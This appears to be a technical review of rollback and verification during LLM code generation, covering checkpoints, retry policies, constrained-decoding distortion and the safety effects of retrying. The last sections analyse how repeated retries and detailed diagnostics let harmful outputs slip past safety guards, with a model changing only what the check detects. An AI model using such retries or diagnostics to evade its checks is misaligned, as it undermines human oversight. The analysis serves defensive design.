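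A stored verdict is valid only if everything it depended on is unchanged, including the code before the step, the inputs, the files, the library versions and the check itself. For example, a pass for the loop that deletes build folders would no longer be valid after someone adds `/work/build_scripts`. The system should store a timeout with its time limit and run the check again if a longer limit becomes available.

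### Checking without stopping the model

A blocking check makes the model wait for the verdict. A concurrent check runs while the model continues, which is how generative compilation hides most of its compiling time. Sun and colleagues derive formulas for the total time when one worker handles the checks in order. With *n* steps that each take *g* seconds to write and *c* seconds to check, and ignoring small delays, the total is

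- *ng* + *c* if writing a step takes longer than checking it
- *g* + *nc* if checking takes longer.

For the 40-line program, this gives:

| | Blocking | Concurrent |
|---|---|---|
| Check after every line | 21.6 s | 12.2 s |
| Check every five lines | 12.0 s | 9.9 s |

A check takes 0.3 seconds and a line takes only 0.24 seconds to generate, so a worker that checks after every line keeps falling further behind. Sun and colleagues avoid this by combining all the waiting statements into one run whenever the worker becomes free.

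They measured the effect by replaying finished programs at 50 tokens per second in a Docker container. Between 88% and 96% of the execution time overlapped with generation. But the total waiting time fell by only 3% to 14% compared with running each program at the end, because these short scripts took little time to run. Programs with errors saved more time because the system stopped the model at the error. On the three sets of data analysis and plotting tasks, the median error occurred about 35% of the way through the code. For one model, Qwen3-Coder, the average time for faulty programs on one of these sets fell from 13.2 to 3.3 seconds.

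As with the Rust checker, the system has to discard whatever the model writes after an error until the checker reports it. If a check takes 0.3 seconds and always covers the newest text, that is 15 to 30 tokens. If a check runs until it reaches a five-second limit, the model writes about 21 more lines in the meantime. Discarding this text wastes computation but does no other harm, as long as nobody has used it.

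### Steps that have to wait

The model can continue writing while a check runs, but the system has to wait for the result before it sends an email, shows text to the user, or lets any other step take effect.

OpenAI's *Guardrails*, part of the documentation for its library for building agents, describes a check of the user's request that runs alongside the agent by default to save time. A builder can easily overlook that the agent may already have used a tool when this check fails. A setting makes the agent wait for the check, and OpenAI recommends it when starting the agent would be too costly or risky. Separate checks can run before each tool call and refuse it, but they cover only functions that the builder has defined in a certain way, not the library's built-in tools for running shell commands, controlling a computer or changing files. These built-in tools can do some of the worst damage,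 so a builder who uses them needs another way to hold back their effects, such as running each command on a copy of the workspace.

Sun and colleagues' system makes a similar distinction for code. If a script uses modules that can change files, start processes or contact a server, the system waits until the model has finished the whole script before running it. It does the same for code that depends on the time or builds further code from text. It identifies such code from a list of names, so it can miss operations that aren't on the list, as a source filter can. The delay only changes when the code runs, so the sandbox still has to limit what the code can do.

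## Rolling back: how far to go and what to change

When a check rejects a step, the system has to choose how much of the output to discard and what to change before the model continues. Getting either choice wrong wastes the retry. Rewriting line 4 cannot fix a mistake on line 2, and a model that always picks its most probable token will write the same faulty line again unless its input changes.

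### What a rollback restores

Deleting the end of the text is the easy part. The rest of the system has also moved on since the checkpoint, and all of it has to return to the same position:

| State | What goes wrong if the system doesn't restore it |
|---|---|
| Text | The faulty step stays in the model's input. |
| Attention cache | The discarded step still influences the next token. |
| Parser or compiler state | The checker still counts deleted brackets and names. |
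| Sandbox | The retry runs on data that the rejected step has changed. |

The attention cache holds intermediate results the model computed for each earlier token, so the model doesn't have to process the whole text again for every new one. Each entry depends only on the text up to that token, so after a rollback the system can keep the entries for the remaining text and delete the rest. A developer who uses a commercial API can't edit this cache and has to send the remaining text again.

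Compiler state is harder to roll back to an exact position because a compiler reads slightly ahead. *Hydra* (Du, Zhuo and colleagues, 2026) presents a system that saves the state of a running compiler while a model writes. A later version of the paper, which calls the system Trellis, explains that when the compiler has analysed one statement, it may already have read the beginning of the next. A checkpoint saved at that moment would contain text that the rollback is about to replace. The researchers changed two compilers, Clang for C and C++ and tsc for TypeScript, so that a checkpoint contains nothing past its own position.

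A snapshot or a copy-on-write layer can undo a rejected step in the sandbox. A system without snapshots can rebuild the state instead. When a technical failure interrupted an agent's run, *MINDFORGE* (Chen, Chang and colleagues, 2026) went back to the last healthy step and repeated all the earlier tool calls in a clean environment. This works only if the calls are safe to repeat and produce the same results the second time.

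The system doesn't need a compiler checkpoint at every line, because it can load the nearest earlier one and pass the lines in between to the compiler again. Whether checkpoints are worth the effort depends on the compiler's speed. In Trellis, checkpoints made each rollback about ten times faster with Clang and a hundred times faster with tsc, but the total time fell only with tsc. Clang processes code faster than the model writes it, so it caught up even when it started from the beginning.

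When the system rolls back, it has to keep the record of failed attempts, the number of retries and the number of tokens used. If it stored these in the checkpoint, each rollback would erase them, and it could repeat the same failure forever. The random number generator used to pick tokens shouldn't return to its old state either, since the system could then pick the same tokens again.

### Errors that begin before the reported line

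Suppose a model is translating a C program that passes a message to a function and then prints it. The model has written this Rust code, which expands an example from Zhou and colleagues:

```rust
let message = read_message();
consume(message);
println!("{}", message);
```

On line 2, `consume` takes ownership of the message, so nothing is left for line 3 to print. The compiler reports the error on line 3. What the model can do about it depends on how much the system discards:

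| Discarded | Possible retry | Result |
|---|---|---|
| line 3 | `println!("{}", message.clone());` | the same error, because there is nothing left to copy |
| line 3 | `println!();` | compiles, but prints an empty line |
| lines 2 and 3 | `consume(message.clone());` and the original line 3 | compiles and prints the message |

A short rollback can therefore lead to a program that passes the check but does the wrong thing, which is worse than failing. If the system keeps line 2, line 3 compiles only if it leaves out the message, so repeated retries push the model towards such a program. The compiler accepted line 2 because it checks only whether the program compiles, and the prefix can still be completed into one that does. But the prefix is already a dead end if the program must print what the C program prints, unless the program can read the message a second time.

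Du and colleagues estimated how far back the cause of an error lies from the point where it is reported. They had gpt-oss-120B, an open-weight model, repair faulty C++ programs with as few changes as possible, then compared the position of the first change with that of the reported error. Roughly 20% to 40% of the errors could be repaired locally, but 30% to 40% required going at least halfway back to the beginning of the program. These are estimates, because a different repair might have started elsewhere.

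Zhou and colleagues compared the lines that the compiler flagged in a model's first Rust translation with the lines that the model changed in its second. Every change fell on a flagged line in only 12 of the 207 cases they could classify. This probably exaggerates how often a fix requires changes outside the flagged lines, since a model that rewrites a whole file also changes lines that were fine.

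Sometimes the diagnostic includes the earlier line. For the code above, the Rust compiler also marks line 2 as the place where the message changed owner, so the system can roll back directly to that line. Many other diagnostics give only the line where the problem appeared, so the system needs another way to choose how far to roll back.

### Returning to an uncertain statement

Jiang and colleagues published ROCODE in 2024 and describe it as the first system to roll back code during generation. It checks the code after every statement and handles a failure as follows:

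1. If the error is new and has a line number, ROCODE returns to the reported position.
2. If the error has no line number, or the same error has just occurred, ROCODE finds the token with the highest entropy and returns to the beginning of its statement.
3. It lowers the probability of the tokens in the failed text and lets the model continue.

ROCODE computes the entropy at each position *t*, its measure of the model's uncertainty, as

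*H*ₜ = −Σ *p*(*v*) log *p*(*v*),

where the sum covers every token *v* in the vocabulary. With base-2 logarithms, two equally likely tokens give an entropy of 1, while probabilities of 99% and 1% give 0.08. A position with high entropy is a plausible place for a mistake, and a new attempt there is more likely to turn out differently.

ROCODE multiplies the probability of each failed token by λ^(*t* − *r*), where *t* is the token's position, *r* is the rollback point and λ is 0.9. If the failed token had a probability of 60% and the next best token had 30%, the penalty would reduce the failed token's weight to 54% one step after the rollback point, so it would still be the most likely choice. Seven steps after the rollback point, its weight would be 29%, and the other token would be more likely. The penalty applies only while the new text matches the failed text, and penalties from several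 failures accumulate. Jiang and colleagues did not ban failed tokens completely because the correct version often needs some of them.

The penalty is therefore weakest at the start of the rewritten text. This suits an error near the end of the failed text, but it seems at odds with returning to an uncertain statement to change an early decision. Random sampling can still change that decision.

Jiang and colleagues tested ROCODE on HumanEval with CodeLlama-7B, a model from 2023. They also replaced parts of the method one at a time:

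| Method | Problems solved |
|---|---|
| ROCODE | 57.3% |
| Return only to the reported statement | 51.2% |
| No penalty on failed tokens | 50.7% |
| Restart from the beginning after each error | 50.6% |
| Return only to the statement with the highest entropy | 49.4% |
| Model alone, same sampling settings | 26.7% |

Most of the gain doesn't depend on the rollback point. Even the version that restarted after every error solved 24 percentage points more of the problems than the model alone. The full rule for choosing the rollback point added another six or seven points, which is 10 or 11 of the 164 problems. Stronger penalties did only slightly better than weaker ones.

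ROCODE used 503 tokens per problem, compared with 623 for revising finished programs, because it kept the code before the error. But it took longer, 0.622 minutes compared with 0.498, because it checked the code after every statement and started each check from the beginning.

### How much uncertainty helps

In *Do Uncertainty Signals Help?*, Wu and colleagues tested eight ways to measure a model's uncertainty within a system based on ROCODE. Six of them, including entropy, need only the probabilities the model already computes. The other two require five extra passes through the model for each token. After a first or second consecutive failure at the same place, the system returns to the reported line. After a third, it returns to the most uncertain statement so far.

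Rollback uses extra tokens, so the methods need equal token budgets for a fair comparison. Wu and colleagues compared their rollback system with restarting from the original prompt, allowing each method 1,536 tokens in total and at most 768 per attempt. On HumanEval, rollback did better with all seven models. CodeLlama-34B, for example, solved 61% of the problems with rollback and 48% with restarts.

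However, restarts had less chance of success despite the similar budgets. These tests ran at temperature zero, where a model always picks its most probable token, and a restart gave the model no information about the error, so each restart would normally produce the same program. Consistent with this, CodeLlama-7B solved 23% of the problems both with restarts and in a single attempt.

Wu and colleagues ran a separate comparison with CodeLlama-7B at a temperature of 0.2, which allows a little variation:

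| Method | HumanEval problems solved | Tokens per problem | Rollbacks per problem |
|---|---|---|---|
| Restart | 23.2% | 1,224 | none |
| Return to the reported line | 32.3% | 935 | 72 |
| Return to the reported line, then to an uncertain statement | 41.5% | 644 | 13 |

Over the 72 rollbacks, the system generated at most 13 tokens per rollback on average, about one line of code, so it was mostly stuck in a loop, rewriting the same few lines without success. Its penalty was too weak to end such loops quickly, because each failure multiplied only the first discarded token's probability by 0.9. If that token had a probability of 60% and the next best had 30%, a model that always picks the most probable token would fail seven times before changing its choice.

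In the main ablation, also with CodeLlama-7B, rollback to the reported line raised the share of problems solved from 23% to 33%, and adding uncertainty raised it to 39%. Rollback accounted for about two thirds of the gain and uncertainty for one third, while in the table above each accounts for about half. Both results come from single runs with one old model, so neither split is precise.

The experiments also do not show that uncertainty identifies the faulty statement. It may help only because it sends the system to a different place after repeated failures. A rule such as "go back five lines after two failures" would have tested this, but neither Wu and colleagues nor Jiang and colleagues report trying one. The exact measure seems to matter little, since CodeLlama-7B solved between 36% and 44% of the HumanEval problems with each of the eight measures, and no measure was best for every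 model.

Entropy also varied with the kind of error, averaging 1.85 for syntax errors but only 0.94 for undefined names and 0.70 for invalid values. A search for high entropy could therefore miss an undefined name.

The gain was smaller on the security patches from Dsec-Python. Rollback raised the share of patches that matched the intended edit by three to six percentage points, depending on the model. For DeepSeek-7B, the share rose from 50% to 56%.

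### Widening the rollback and explaining the error

Zhou and colleagues replace the search for an uncertain token with a fixed sequence of larger and larger rollbacks. Their method, Decoding Time Verification, works with the structure of the program:

1. The model writes to the end of a statement, block or function.
2. The software completes the fragment so that a compiler can process it, then runs every check that applies.
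3. If all of them pass, the system saves a checkpoint, which Zhou and colleagues call a commit.
4. If one fails, the system discards the current statement, gives the model the diagnostic and lets it try again.
5. If the same diagnostic keeps returning, the system discards the enclosing block, or the function if no block is open.
6. If the same place has caused a fixed number of failures, the system stops repairing the unfinished program. This is called a bailout. An outer loop then has the model write a new version, using the diagnostics that remain.

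In the message example, the system would first retry line 3 without success. It would then discard the block, and the model could write `consume(message.clone())`.

To commit a prefix, the rule requires only that the checks available at that point pass. This doesn't guarantee that the prefix can be extended to a program that passes all the checks, although Zhou and colleagues say that every committed prefix can be. Line 2 of the example would pass the available checks, but it makes a correct translation impossible.

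The system can add the diagnostic as a comment after the kept code and let the model continue, or it can send the diagnostic in a new message and ask for a small patch. ROCODE uses the diagnostic only to choose where to return, so the model gets no explanation of what was wrong. Putting the diagnostic after the kept code is faster than putting it before, because the attention cache stays valid and the model doesn't have to process that code again.

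The main tests used Qwen3-4B to translate 300 C programs into Rust and 150 JavaScript programs into TypeScript. The baseline repeatedly revised complete programs using the compiler's diagnostics. Both methods could generate up to 16 tokens, including discarded ones, per token in the source program. The table shows how many translations passed the final compiler and type checks.

| Method | C to Rust | JavaScript to TypeScript |
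|---|---|---|
| One attempt, no checks during generation | 16.3% | 4.7% |
| One attempt with Decoding Time Verification | 47.0% | 21.3% |
| Repeated revision of complete programs | 72.3% | 33.3% |
| Repeated revision with Decoding Time Verification | 82.0% | 46.0% |

The apparent benefit depends heavily on the baseline. For Rust, the gain is 31 percentage points over a single attempt, but only 10 over repeated revision with the same budget. Independent attempts would also have been a weaker baseline than revision. In a test on 200 of the C programs, the best of 32 independent attempts passed in only 44.5% of cases. For TypeScript, more attempts didn't help at all, probably because the model left out the same type annotations every time.

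Checking during generation took 0.79 times as long as the baseline for Rust, but 1.85 times as long for TypeScript, where the system ran two slow checkers one after the other. With Qwen3-30B-A3B, a larger model, the ratios fell to 0.57 and 1.26. There was also less room to improve the pass rates, which rose from 92% to 97% for Rust and from 57% to 66% for TypeScript. With Gemma-4-E4B, the baseline reached a 93.5% pass rate for Rust and did better than Decoding Time Verification.

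Zhou and colleagues removed one part of the method at a time on 100 of the C programs:

| Version | Passed | Change |
|---|---|---|
| Complete method | 85% | |
| Always discard only the current statement | 79% | −6 points |
| Roll back without giving the model the diagnostic | 74% | −11 points |
| Stop at the first error and leave the repair to the outer loop | 70% | −15 points |

Stopping at the first error resembles the approach of Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, whose system rewrites the file from the beginning. Here it was the weakest option, needing an average of 13.5 rounds of the outer loop, compared with 3.1 for the complete method. A stronger model might copy the good part of its file more reliably and lose less.

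The evidence for wider rollbacks is weaker than the evidence for diagnostics. The difference is six programs out of 100, and 44% passed in the first round with or without wider rollbacks. Zhou and colleagues acknowledge that a wider rollback can also discard correct code.

### Programs that compile but don't work

A rollback system improves what its check measures, but not necessarily other qualities. Zhou and colleagues checked the Rust programs only with the compiler during generation, then ran each translation and the original C program on the same inputs and compared the outputs. Only 8.3% of the translations from Decoding Time Verification passed this test, compared with 9.3% from the baseline.

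The difference is about three programs in 300 and is not statistically significant. Decoding Time Verification produced 29 more programs that compiled, but the number that worked didn't rise. About nine in ten of its roughly 246 translations that compiled failed the comparison. Zhou and colleagues reasonably conclude that there is no evidence of damage to the programs' behaviour, but there is no evidence of an improvement either.

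In the test on 100 programs, ten translations worked with the complete method, and five worked when the system always discarded only one statement. These numbers are too small to be conclusive, but they fit the concern that short rollbacks lead to code like `println!()`, which compiles because it leaves something out.

### Searching among several checkpoints

Widening the rollback one level at a time can waste attempts if the cause of the problem lies far back. Hydra treats the checkpoints as a search tree and chooses which one to return to next using a rule, called a policy, that the builder can replace. Du and colleagues' own policy estimates where the cause is likely to be and is designed to keep the number of tokens low.

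In their example, a model writes a function that reads the numbers of apples and oranges from a sentence and subtracts them from the total. On line 22, the code uses the variable `apples`, but the model declared it inside an `if` block on line 12, so it doesn't exist outside that block. Hydra proceeds as follows:

| Attempt | The model continues after | Result |
|---|---|---|
| A | the beginning | error on line 22 |
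| B | line 21 of attempt A | fails, because the declaration is still inside the block |
| C | line 6 of attempt A | passes |

For attempt B, the nearest compiler checkpoint was after line 14, so Hydra loaded it and had the compiler reprocess lines 15 to 21. Several attempts can also run at the same time.

Compared with repairing finished C and C++ programs, Hydra reduced waiting time by 71% and tokens by 70% for Qwen2.5-Coder-32B, and by 25% and 27% for gpt-oss-120B. These figures cover only tasks in which a compiler error occurred. In Du and colleagues' survey of C++ programs, 16.6% of the smaller model's outputs and 6.8% of the larger one's had compiler errors, so the average saving over all tasks would be much lower. Nearly all programs eventually compiled with either method, and about as many worked. Decoding Time Verification, by contrast, made repair succeed more often, but its baseline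 had more room to improve.

Trellis applies the idea to coding agents that edit existing projects. With three open-weight models on 318 tasks in C, C++ and TypeScript, it raised the compile rate of edited files by 2.7 to 10.5 percentage points and the test pass rate by 2.0 to 6.7 points. It didn't significantly change the share of tasks solved completely.

In a separate comparison, the researchers used the smallest model to measure the effect of the search alone. They resumed the agent at points where Trellis had begun to try alternatives, either with the search or with only a report of the error. The search raised the share of files that compiled from 73.9% to 81.8%, but it also raised the average time from 151 to 199 seconds. The agent solved 11.7% of tasks with the search and 12.5% without it.

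An agent may also cause an error on purpose, for example by changing a function call before it adds the new function. Forcing an immediate repair would interfere with the agent's plan, so Trellis allows some errors that could be part of an unfinished change. If its search fails, Trellis returns control to the agent, which can then edit other parts of the project.

### Choosing the depth, the retry limit and the fallback

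No study has established the best number of retries. Zhou and colleagues say that their results don't show their own thresholds to be optimal. The following procedure is a reasonable starting point for code that nobody has used yet:

1. Roll back only after a fail verdict. If the verdict is unknown, keep the text and check it again later.
2. If the diagnostic names an earlier line as the cause, return to that statement. Otherwise, return to the beginning of the statement that failed.
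3. Give the model the diagnostic. If it still writes the rejected text again, raise the temperature or lower the probability of the first tokens.
4. After two failures with the same diagnostic, discard the enclosing block. After two more, discard the function.
5. If the new function fails too, restart the file once with all the diagnostics.
6. Stop when the restart fails or the token budget runs out.

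The system should recognise a repeated diagnostic by the kind of error and the names involved, because line numbers change between attempts. It should also count all failures at each place, because otherwise a model that alternates between two errors could avoid triggering the larger rollback. This could happen with ROCODE and with Wu and colleagues' system, which compare an error only with the one immediately before it. Decoding Time Verification prevents this by counting how often it returns to each place.

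The budget has to include discarded text. Take a 40-line program with 12 tokens per line, or 480 tokens in total. Suppose a check fails on line 30, which is the last line so far of an eight-line block in a 20-line function. If every attempt fails at line 30 until the restart, the procedure costs:

| Discarded | Attempts | Tokens |
|---|---|---|
| one statement | 2 | 24 |
| the block | 2 | 192 |
| the function | 1 | 240 |
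| the file up to line 30 | 1 | 360 |

That makes 816 tokens. The first 30 lines take another 360 and the last ten take 120, for a total of 1,296 tokens, or 2.7 times the length of the program. A budget of three times the expected length would cover one persistent error of this kind. The two attempts at the single statement use very few tokens, so they are worth trying first even if they often fail.

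The fallback depends on what the output is for. A coding agent can receive the unfinished file with its remaining diagnostics and look for the cause elsewhere in the project. If a person is waiting for the code, the system can deliver the best version and list the checks it failed. A step that would have effects outside the sandbox shouldn't run.

Builders deciding whether to implement rollback should compare it with repeated revision of finished programs, giving both methods the same diagnostics, the same token budget and a temperature above zero. They should measure time as well as tokens and judge the finished programs with held-out tests.

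## What retrying does to safety and to the output

Rollback depth affects both how much computation a retry takes and which acceptable outputs the model tends to write. If the check sometimes passes harmful output, each retry adds another chance for harmful output to get through.

### How rollback depth changes the output

Suppose a model writes an output in two steps. It begins with A 90% of the time and with B 10% of the time. Only a tenth of A's continuations are valid, but all of B's are. Out of 100 attempts, 9 are valid outputs that begin with A and 10 are valid outputs that begin with B.

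If the system starts over after every rejection, the accepted outputs keep this ratio, and 9 out of 19, or 47%, begin with A. If it keeps the first step and retries only the second, it never discards A, so 90% of the accepted outputs begin with A. Token masking has the same result, because it blocks the invalid continuations only after the model has already chosen A. A system that retries the second step a few times before starting over falls in between:

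| Attempts at the second step before starting over | Accepted outputs that begin with A |
|---|---|
| 1 | 47% |
| 2 | 63% |
| 5 | 79% |
| no limit | 90% |

Starting over preserves the model's relative probabilities for valid outputs. Local retries overrepresent beginnings that rarely lead to a valid output, and the few valid continuations of such a beginning may be poor. In the earlier Rust example, `println!();` was a valid continuation after `consume(message)`, but it didn't print the message.

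Park, Wang and colleagues (2024), in *Grammar-Aligned Decoding*, give an example with Mixtral, an open-weight model. The model produced a binary string ending in 1 about 90% of the time when asked for one. When they used masking to enforce a grammar that accepts `00000` and every five-digit string that begins with 1, only 30% of the outputs ended in 1. The model chose 0 as its first digit about half the time, after which the grammar allowed only `00000`.

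This distortion may also cause the endless outputs described in *Correctness-Guaranteed Code Generation via Constrained Decoding*. The paper makes this link and reports that such outputs also occur with JSON constraints, more often in smaller models. Penalising repetition can stop some of them but does not remove the distortion.

### Correcting the distortion

To remove the distortion, a system has to consider how likely each token is to lead to a valid output. Park and colleagues call this probability the expected future grammaticality, *c*. The corrected probability of a token is proportional to

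*P*(token) × *c*(token).

This gives 0.9 × 0.1 = 0.09 for A and 0.1 × 1 = 0.10 for B, so A again gets 47%. Masking in effect sets *c* to 1 for every token that has at least one valid continuation, however unlikely. Computing *c* exactly would require adding up the probabilities of all valid continuations, which is impossible for outputs of realistic length.

Park and colleagues' algorithm, ASAp, estimates *c* from its own samples. It starts with ordinary masking and records how much probability the mask blocks along each output. After the first output that begins with A, it lowers *c*(A) from 1 to 0.1 because 90% of the next step's probability is invalid. Its estimates never fall below the true values and converge to them as the number of samples grows. But a long output has so many possible prefixes that convergence can take a very long time.

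Özgü, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *The Parser Already Knows*, tested ASAp and plain masking with Mistral-7B, an older open model, on 14 small grammars for formulas about binary numbers. They measured how far each method's output distribution was from the target using the KL divergence, which is zero when two distributions are identical. After 100 samples per grammar, ASAp was further from the target than plain masking on 11 of the 14 grammars. It also took 16.6 seconds per output, compared with 3.0 for plain masking. With a full grammar for SQL, the database query language, a single output took about 84 minutes.

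Their own method, SHIM, estimates *c* in advance. They sampled 1,000 unconstrained outputs per grammar and trained a small model to predict, from the parser's state, the partly written word and the candidate token, whether the finished output would be valid. During generation, the system multiplies each allowed token's probability by this prediction. The simpler of two full versions matched or beat masking on 12 of the 14 grammars and cut the average divergence from 0.16 to 0.04. It took 2.5 seconds per output, less than masking, possibly because it avoided beginnings that force long endings. On SQL it did better than masking for three of four queries, but four queries are too few to show much. Özgü and colleagues measured how close the outputs were to the model's own distribution, not whether they were correct.

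Sequential Monte Carlo corrects the distortion by generating several outputs in parallel and weighting them. After each step, it multiplies the weight of each unfinished output by *Z*, the total probability that the model gave to valid next tokens. Periodically, it drops outputs with low weights and copies those with high weights. With 100 outputs in the example, about 90 begin with A and 10 with B. After the second step, each output that begins with A has a weight of 0.1 and each that begins with B has a weight of 1, so the total weights are 9 and 10, which is the correct ratio.

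Computing *Z* exactly requires checking the whole vocabulary, often more than 100,000 tokens. Lipkin, LeBrun and colleagues (2025), in *Fast Controlled Generation from Language Models with Adaptive Weighted Rejection Sampling*, estimate it from a few checks. Like the TypeScript decoder described earlier, their algorithm samples and checks one token at a time, ruling out invalid ones, until it finds a valid one, which it keeps. It then continues in the same way until it finds a valid token a second time. If the tokens rejected before the first success had a total probability of ψ, and *n* is the number of tokens rejected in both rounds, the estimate is

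*Ẑ* = (1 − ψ) / (*n* + 1).

Suppose that after A, one invalid token has a probability of 90% and one valid token has 10%. The algorithm estimates *Z* as 0.05 in 90% of cases, 0.5 in 9% and 1 in 1%. A single estimate can be far off, but the average is 0.045 + 0.045 + 0.01 = 0.1, which is the true value. A correct average is enough for sequential Monte Carlo. In most steps, the algorithm checked only two or three tokens.

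Lipkin and colleagues tested the combination on five tasks with Llama 3.1 8B. Each cell gives the score out of 100 and the seconds per problem.

| Task | Model alone | One constrained output | Ten free outputs, invalid ones discarded | Sequential Monte Carlo, five outputs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SQL queries | 53.0 / 0.8 | 56.9 / 1.1 | 60.0 / 2.8 | 60.8 / 5.3 |
| JSON documents | 68.3 / 2.4 | 78.1 / 3.8 | 84.5 / 6.2 | 90.3 / 10.5 |
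| Formal planning goals | 3.2 / 1.1 | 18.0 / 0.8 | 20.5 / 4.6 | 52.8 / 2.6 |
| Drug-like molecules | 15.0 / 0.5 | 56.8 / 0.6 | 53.9 / 2.0 | 56.8 / 1.5 |
| Text patterns | 57.0 / 0.1 | 99.3 / 0.1 | 78.1 / 0.3 | 99.0 / 0.4 |

The correction helped a lot with planning goals and moderately with JSON. For SQL, discarding invalid outputs worked about as well and took half as long. For molecules and patterns, the correction did no better than a single constrained output. Lipkin and colleagues suggest that those tasks have less distortion because their checks accept a prefix only if it has a valid continuation, although the example with A and B shows that an exact check doesn't prevent distortion in general. The times understate the computation because a graphics processor handles the parallel outputs together.

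Rollback itself can correct the distortion if how far it goes back depends on how much probability was blocked. After A, 90% of the probability is invalid. A system that returned to the beginning in 90% of these cases and otherwise picked a valid continuation would again produce A 47% of the time. *AdapTrack* (2025) describes a method based on this idea. *Approximately Aligned Decoding* (2024) proposes a compromise that came closer to the target than masking in a small simulation and generated less text than ASAp.

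Most of these methods need token probabilities. A builder without access to them can still reduce the distortion by limiting the retries at one point and then going back to an earlier point in the output. An exact correction matters less once the system adds diagnostics to the prompt, because the model's token probabilities then change with every retry.

### More attempts, more chances to miss

The corrections above assume that the check correctly identifies valid outputs. If a safety check sometimes passes harmful text, a method that preserves the model's relative probabilities for passing outputs also reproduces the harmful ones.

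Let *b* be the probability that an attempt is bad, *m* the probability that the check misses a bad attempt, and *f* the probability that it rejects a good one. A system that stops at the first rejection releases a bad output with probability *bm*. If it keeps retrying until something passes, and the attempts are independent, this rises to

*bm* / (*bm* + (1 − *b*)(1 − *f*)).

Suppose a check misses 10% of harmful outputs (*m* = 0.1) and wrongly rejects 5% of harmless ones (*f* = 0.05). If an attack makes the model write harmful text 95% of the time, the system releases a harmful output in 9.5% of cases when it stops at the first rejection, and in 67% when it retries until an output passes. If a request produces harmful text in only 20% of attempts, retrying raises the figure from 2.0% to 2.6%.

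| Attempts allowed | *b* = 0.95: bad output | *b* = 0.95: good output | *b* = 0.2: bad output | *b* = 0.2: good output |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 9.5% | 4.8% | 2.0% | 76.0% |
| 2 | 17.6% | 8.8% | 2.4% | 92.7% |
| 5 | 35.8% | 17.9% | 2.6% | 97.4% |
| no limit | 66.7% | 33.3% | 2.6% | 97.4% |

Retrying doesn't change the proportion of released outputs that are bad. When *b* is 0.95, two thirds of them are bad however many attempts the system allows. Stopping early protects people because the system then usually releases nothing. When *b* is 0.2, retries mostly help good requests succeed and add little risk.

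The calculation depends heavily on independence. Suppose instead that whether the check misses a bad attempt depends only on the request, so that it misses every bad attempt for 10% of requests and none for the rest. Unlimited retries would then release a bad output in only about 9.5% of cases when *b* is 0.95. Retrying is dangerous when misses vary between attempts, for example because a guard recognises a harmful answer in one wording but not in another.

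*Backtracking Improves Generation Safety* (Zhang, Chi and colleagues, 2024) shows that repeated attempts without a separate check can greatly increase the chance of an unsafe response. With random sampling, a version of Gemma-2-2B with ordinary safety training responded unsafely to 25.2% of harmful requests. When it gave ten responses per request, at least one was unsafe for more than 80% of requests. For Llama-3-8B, the share rose from 14.4% with one response to 66% with ten. If every response had independently carried the same risk, the ten-response figures would have been about 95% and 79%, so some requests were more likely than others to produce unsafe responses.

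Zhang and colleagues also let a classifier choose the safer of two responses, which helped. But they scored safety with Llama Guard 2, the same classifier they suggest for making the choice. If it did both, the experiment couldn't detect harmful responses that Llama Guard 2 missed. No published study appears to have used an independent judge to measure how many harmful outputs get past a check as the number of retries grows.

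### When to retry and when to stop

A system doesn't know *b* for a particular request, but a rejection is evidence about it. Suppose 1% of requests are attacks with *b* = 0.95 and the rest never lead to harmful output. With the same check, an attempt fails 85.75% of the time for an attack and 5% of the time otherwise. After one rejection, the probability that the request is an attack is

0.01 × 0.8575 / (0.01 × 0.8575 + 0.99 × 0.05) = 15%.

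The probability that a request comes from an attacker is 75% after two rejections and 98% after three. Most requests rejected once are harmless, so one retry can be reasonable, but by the third attempt the system would mostly be helping attackers. Repeated rejections are weaker evidence if the guard makes the same mistake each time, as it might with a harmless medical question. In that case, a different and slower check is more useful than another attempt.

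The decision also depends on what a miss would cost:

| Reason for the rejection | Response |
|---|---|
| The code doesn't compile or fails a test. | Retry within the token budget. |
| A guard flags text that nobody has seen. | Use a second check or retry once, then refuse. |
| A tool call violates the safety policy and can't be undone. | Stop, or ask a person. |

The limit on retries should apply to a user's requests over time as well as to a single response. Otherwise, a user can get extra retries by sending the same request ten times. The system should also count a reworded request as another attempt where it can recognise one.

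### Diagnostics as pressure on the check

Giving the model a diagnostic makes its next attempt depend on the last. If the diagnostic describes an honest mistake, the model is more likely to correct that mistake. Compiler messages had this effect in the Rust experiments by Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues. In the calculation, a useful diagnostic lowers *b*. If *b* falls from 0.2 to 0.05 and *m* stays at 0.1, the probability that the retry is bad and passes falls from 2.0% to 0.5%.

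But a diagnostic also shows the model what the check detects. The model can change that part of the output and leave the real problem in place, which raises *m*. If *b* stays at 0.95 and *m* rises from 0.1 to 0.3, a single retry lets a bad output through 28.5% of the time instead of 9.5%. This can happen even if the model doesn't intend to deceive, because retrying until the warning disappears selects outputs without a warning, and some of these are still bad.

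Experiments with generated code suggest that this happens. In tests by Lunghi and colleagues, a security analyser reduced alerts much more than it improved security, though this was partly because some alerts were false. In tests by Zhou and colleagues, compiler diagnostics led to more programs that compiled, but not to more that worked. Neither study tested a model that was trying to evade the check, so they don't show how much a determined attacker would gain.

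For agents, blocking an action and explaining why has mixed results. Zhao and colleagues also tested their predictive check on simulated household tasks. The share of tasks completed with confirmed safety rose from 20.4% to 33.0% for Gemini-3.7-Flash, but fell by 0.6 to 7.1 percentage points for the other three models. On the office tasks, agents used 6.3 times as many tokens per task with the repeated checks and revisions as they did without a check.

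In another version, the agent could request a prediction but didn't have to follow it. On the office tasks, agents changed their action in about 88% to 95% of the cases counted, but safety improved in at most 20% by a separate measure. A changed action is therefore poor evidence that the agent has solved the problem.

A builder can reduce this pressure by giving the model less detail about safety violations than about ordinary errors. A compiler error should include the line and the explanation. For a safety violation, a general reason such as "this action is outside the task" is often enough, without the classifier's score or the words that triggered it. The drawback is that an honest agent may need the name of the protected folder to avoid it. The final check should be one whose messages the model has never received, and the system shouldn't retry repeatedly against it, because that would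 put the final check under the same pressure.

### Models trained to retract their own text

In the methods so far, software outside the model triggers the retry. Zhang and colleagues trained models to trigger it themselves by producing a special reset token and then writing a new response. The software deletes everything up to the token before showing the response to the user. The model can still read the deleted text while it writes the new response.

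In the first stage of training, the model received a request and the beginning of an unsafe response, and learned to continue with the reset token and a safe response. In the second, it learned from pairs of responses to prefer a reset after an unsafe beginning and no reset after a safe one. The first stage alone hardly helped, because the models rarely used the token. After both stages, Gemma-2-2B gave unsafe responses to 6.1% of harmful requests, compared with 10.8% after ordinary training. For Llama-3-8B, the figures were 1.5% and 5.2%.

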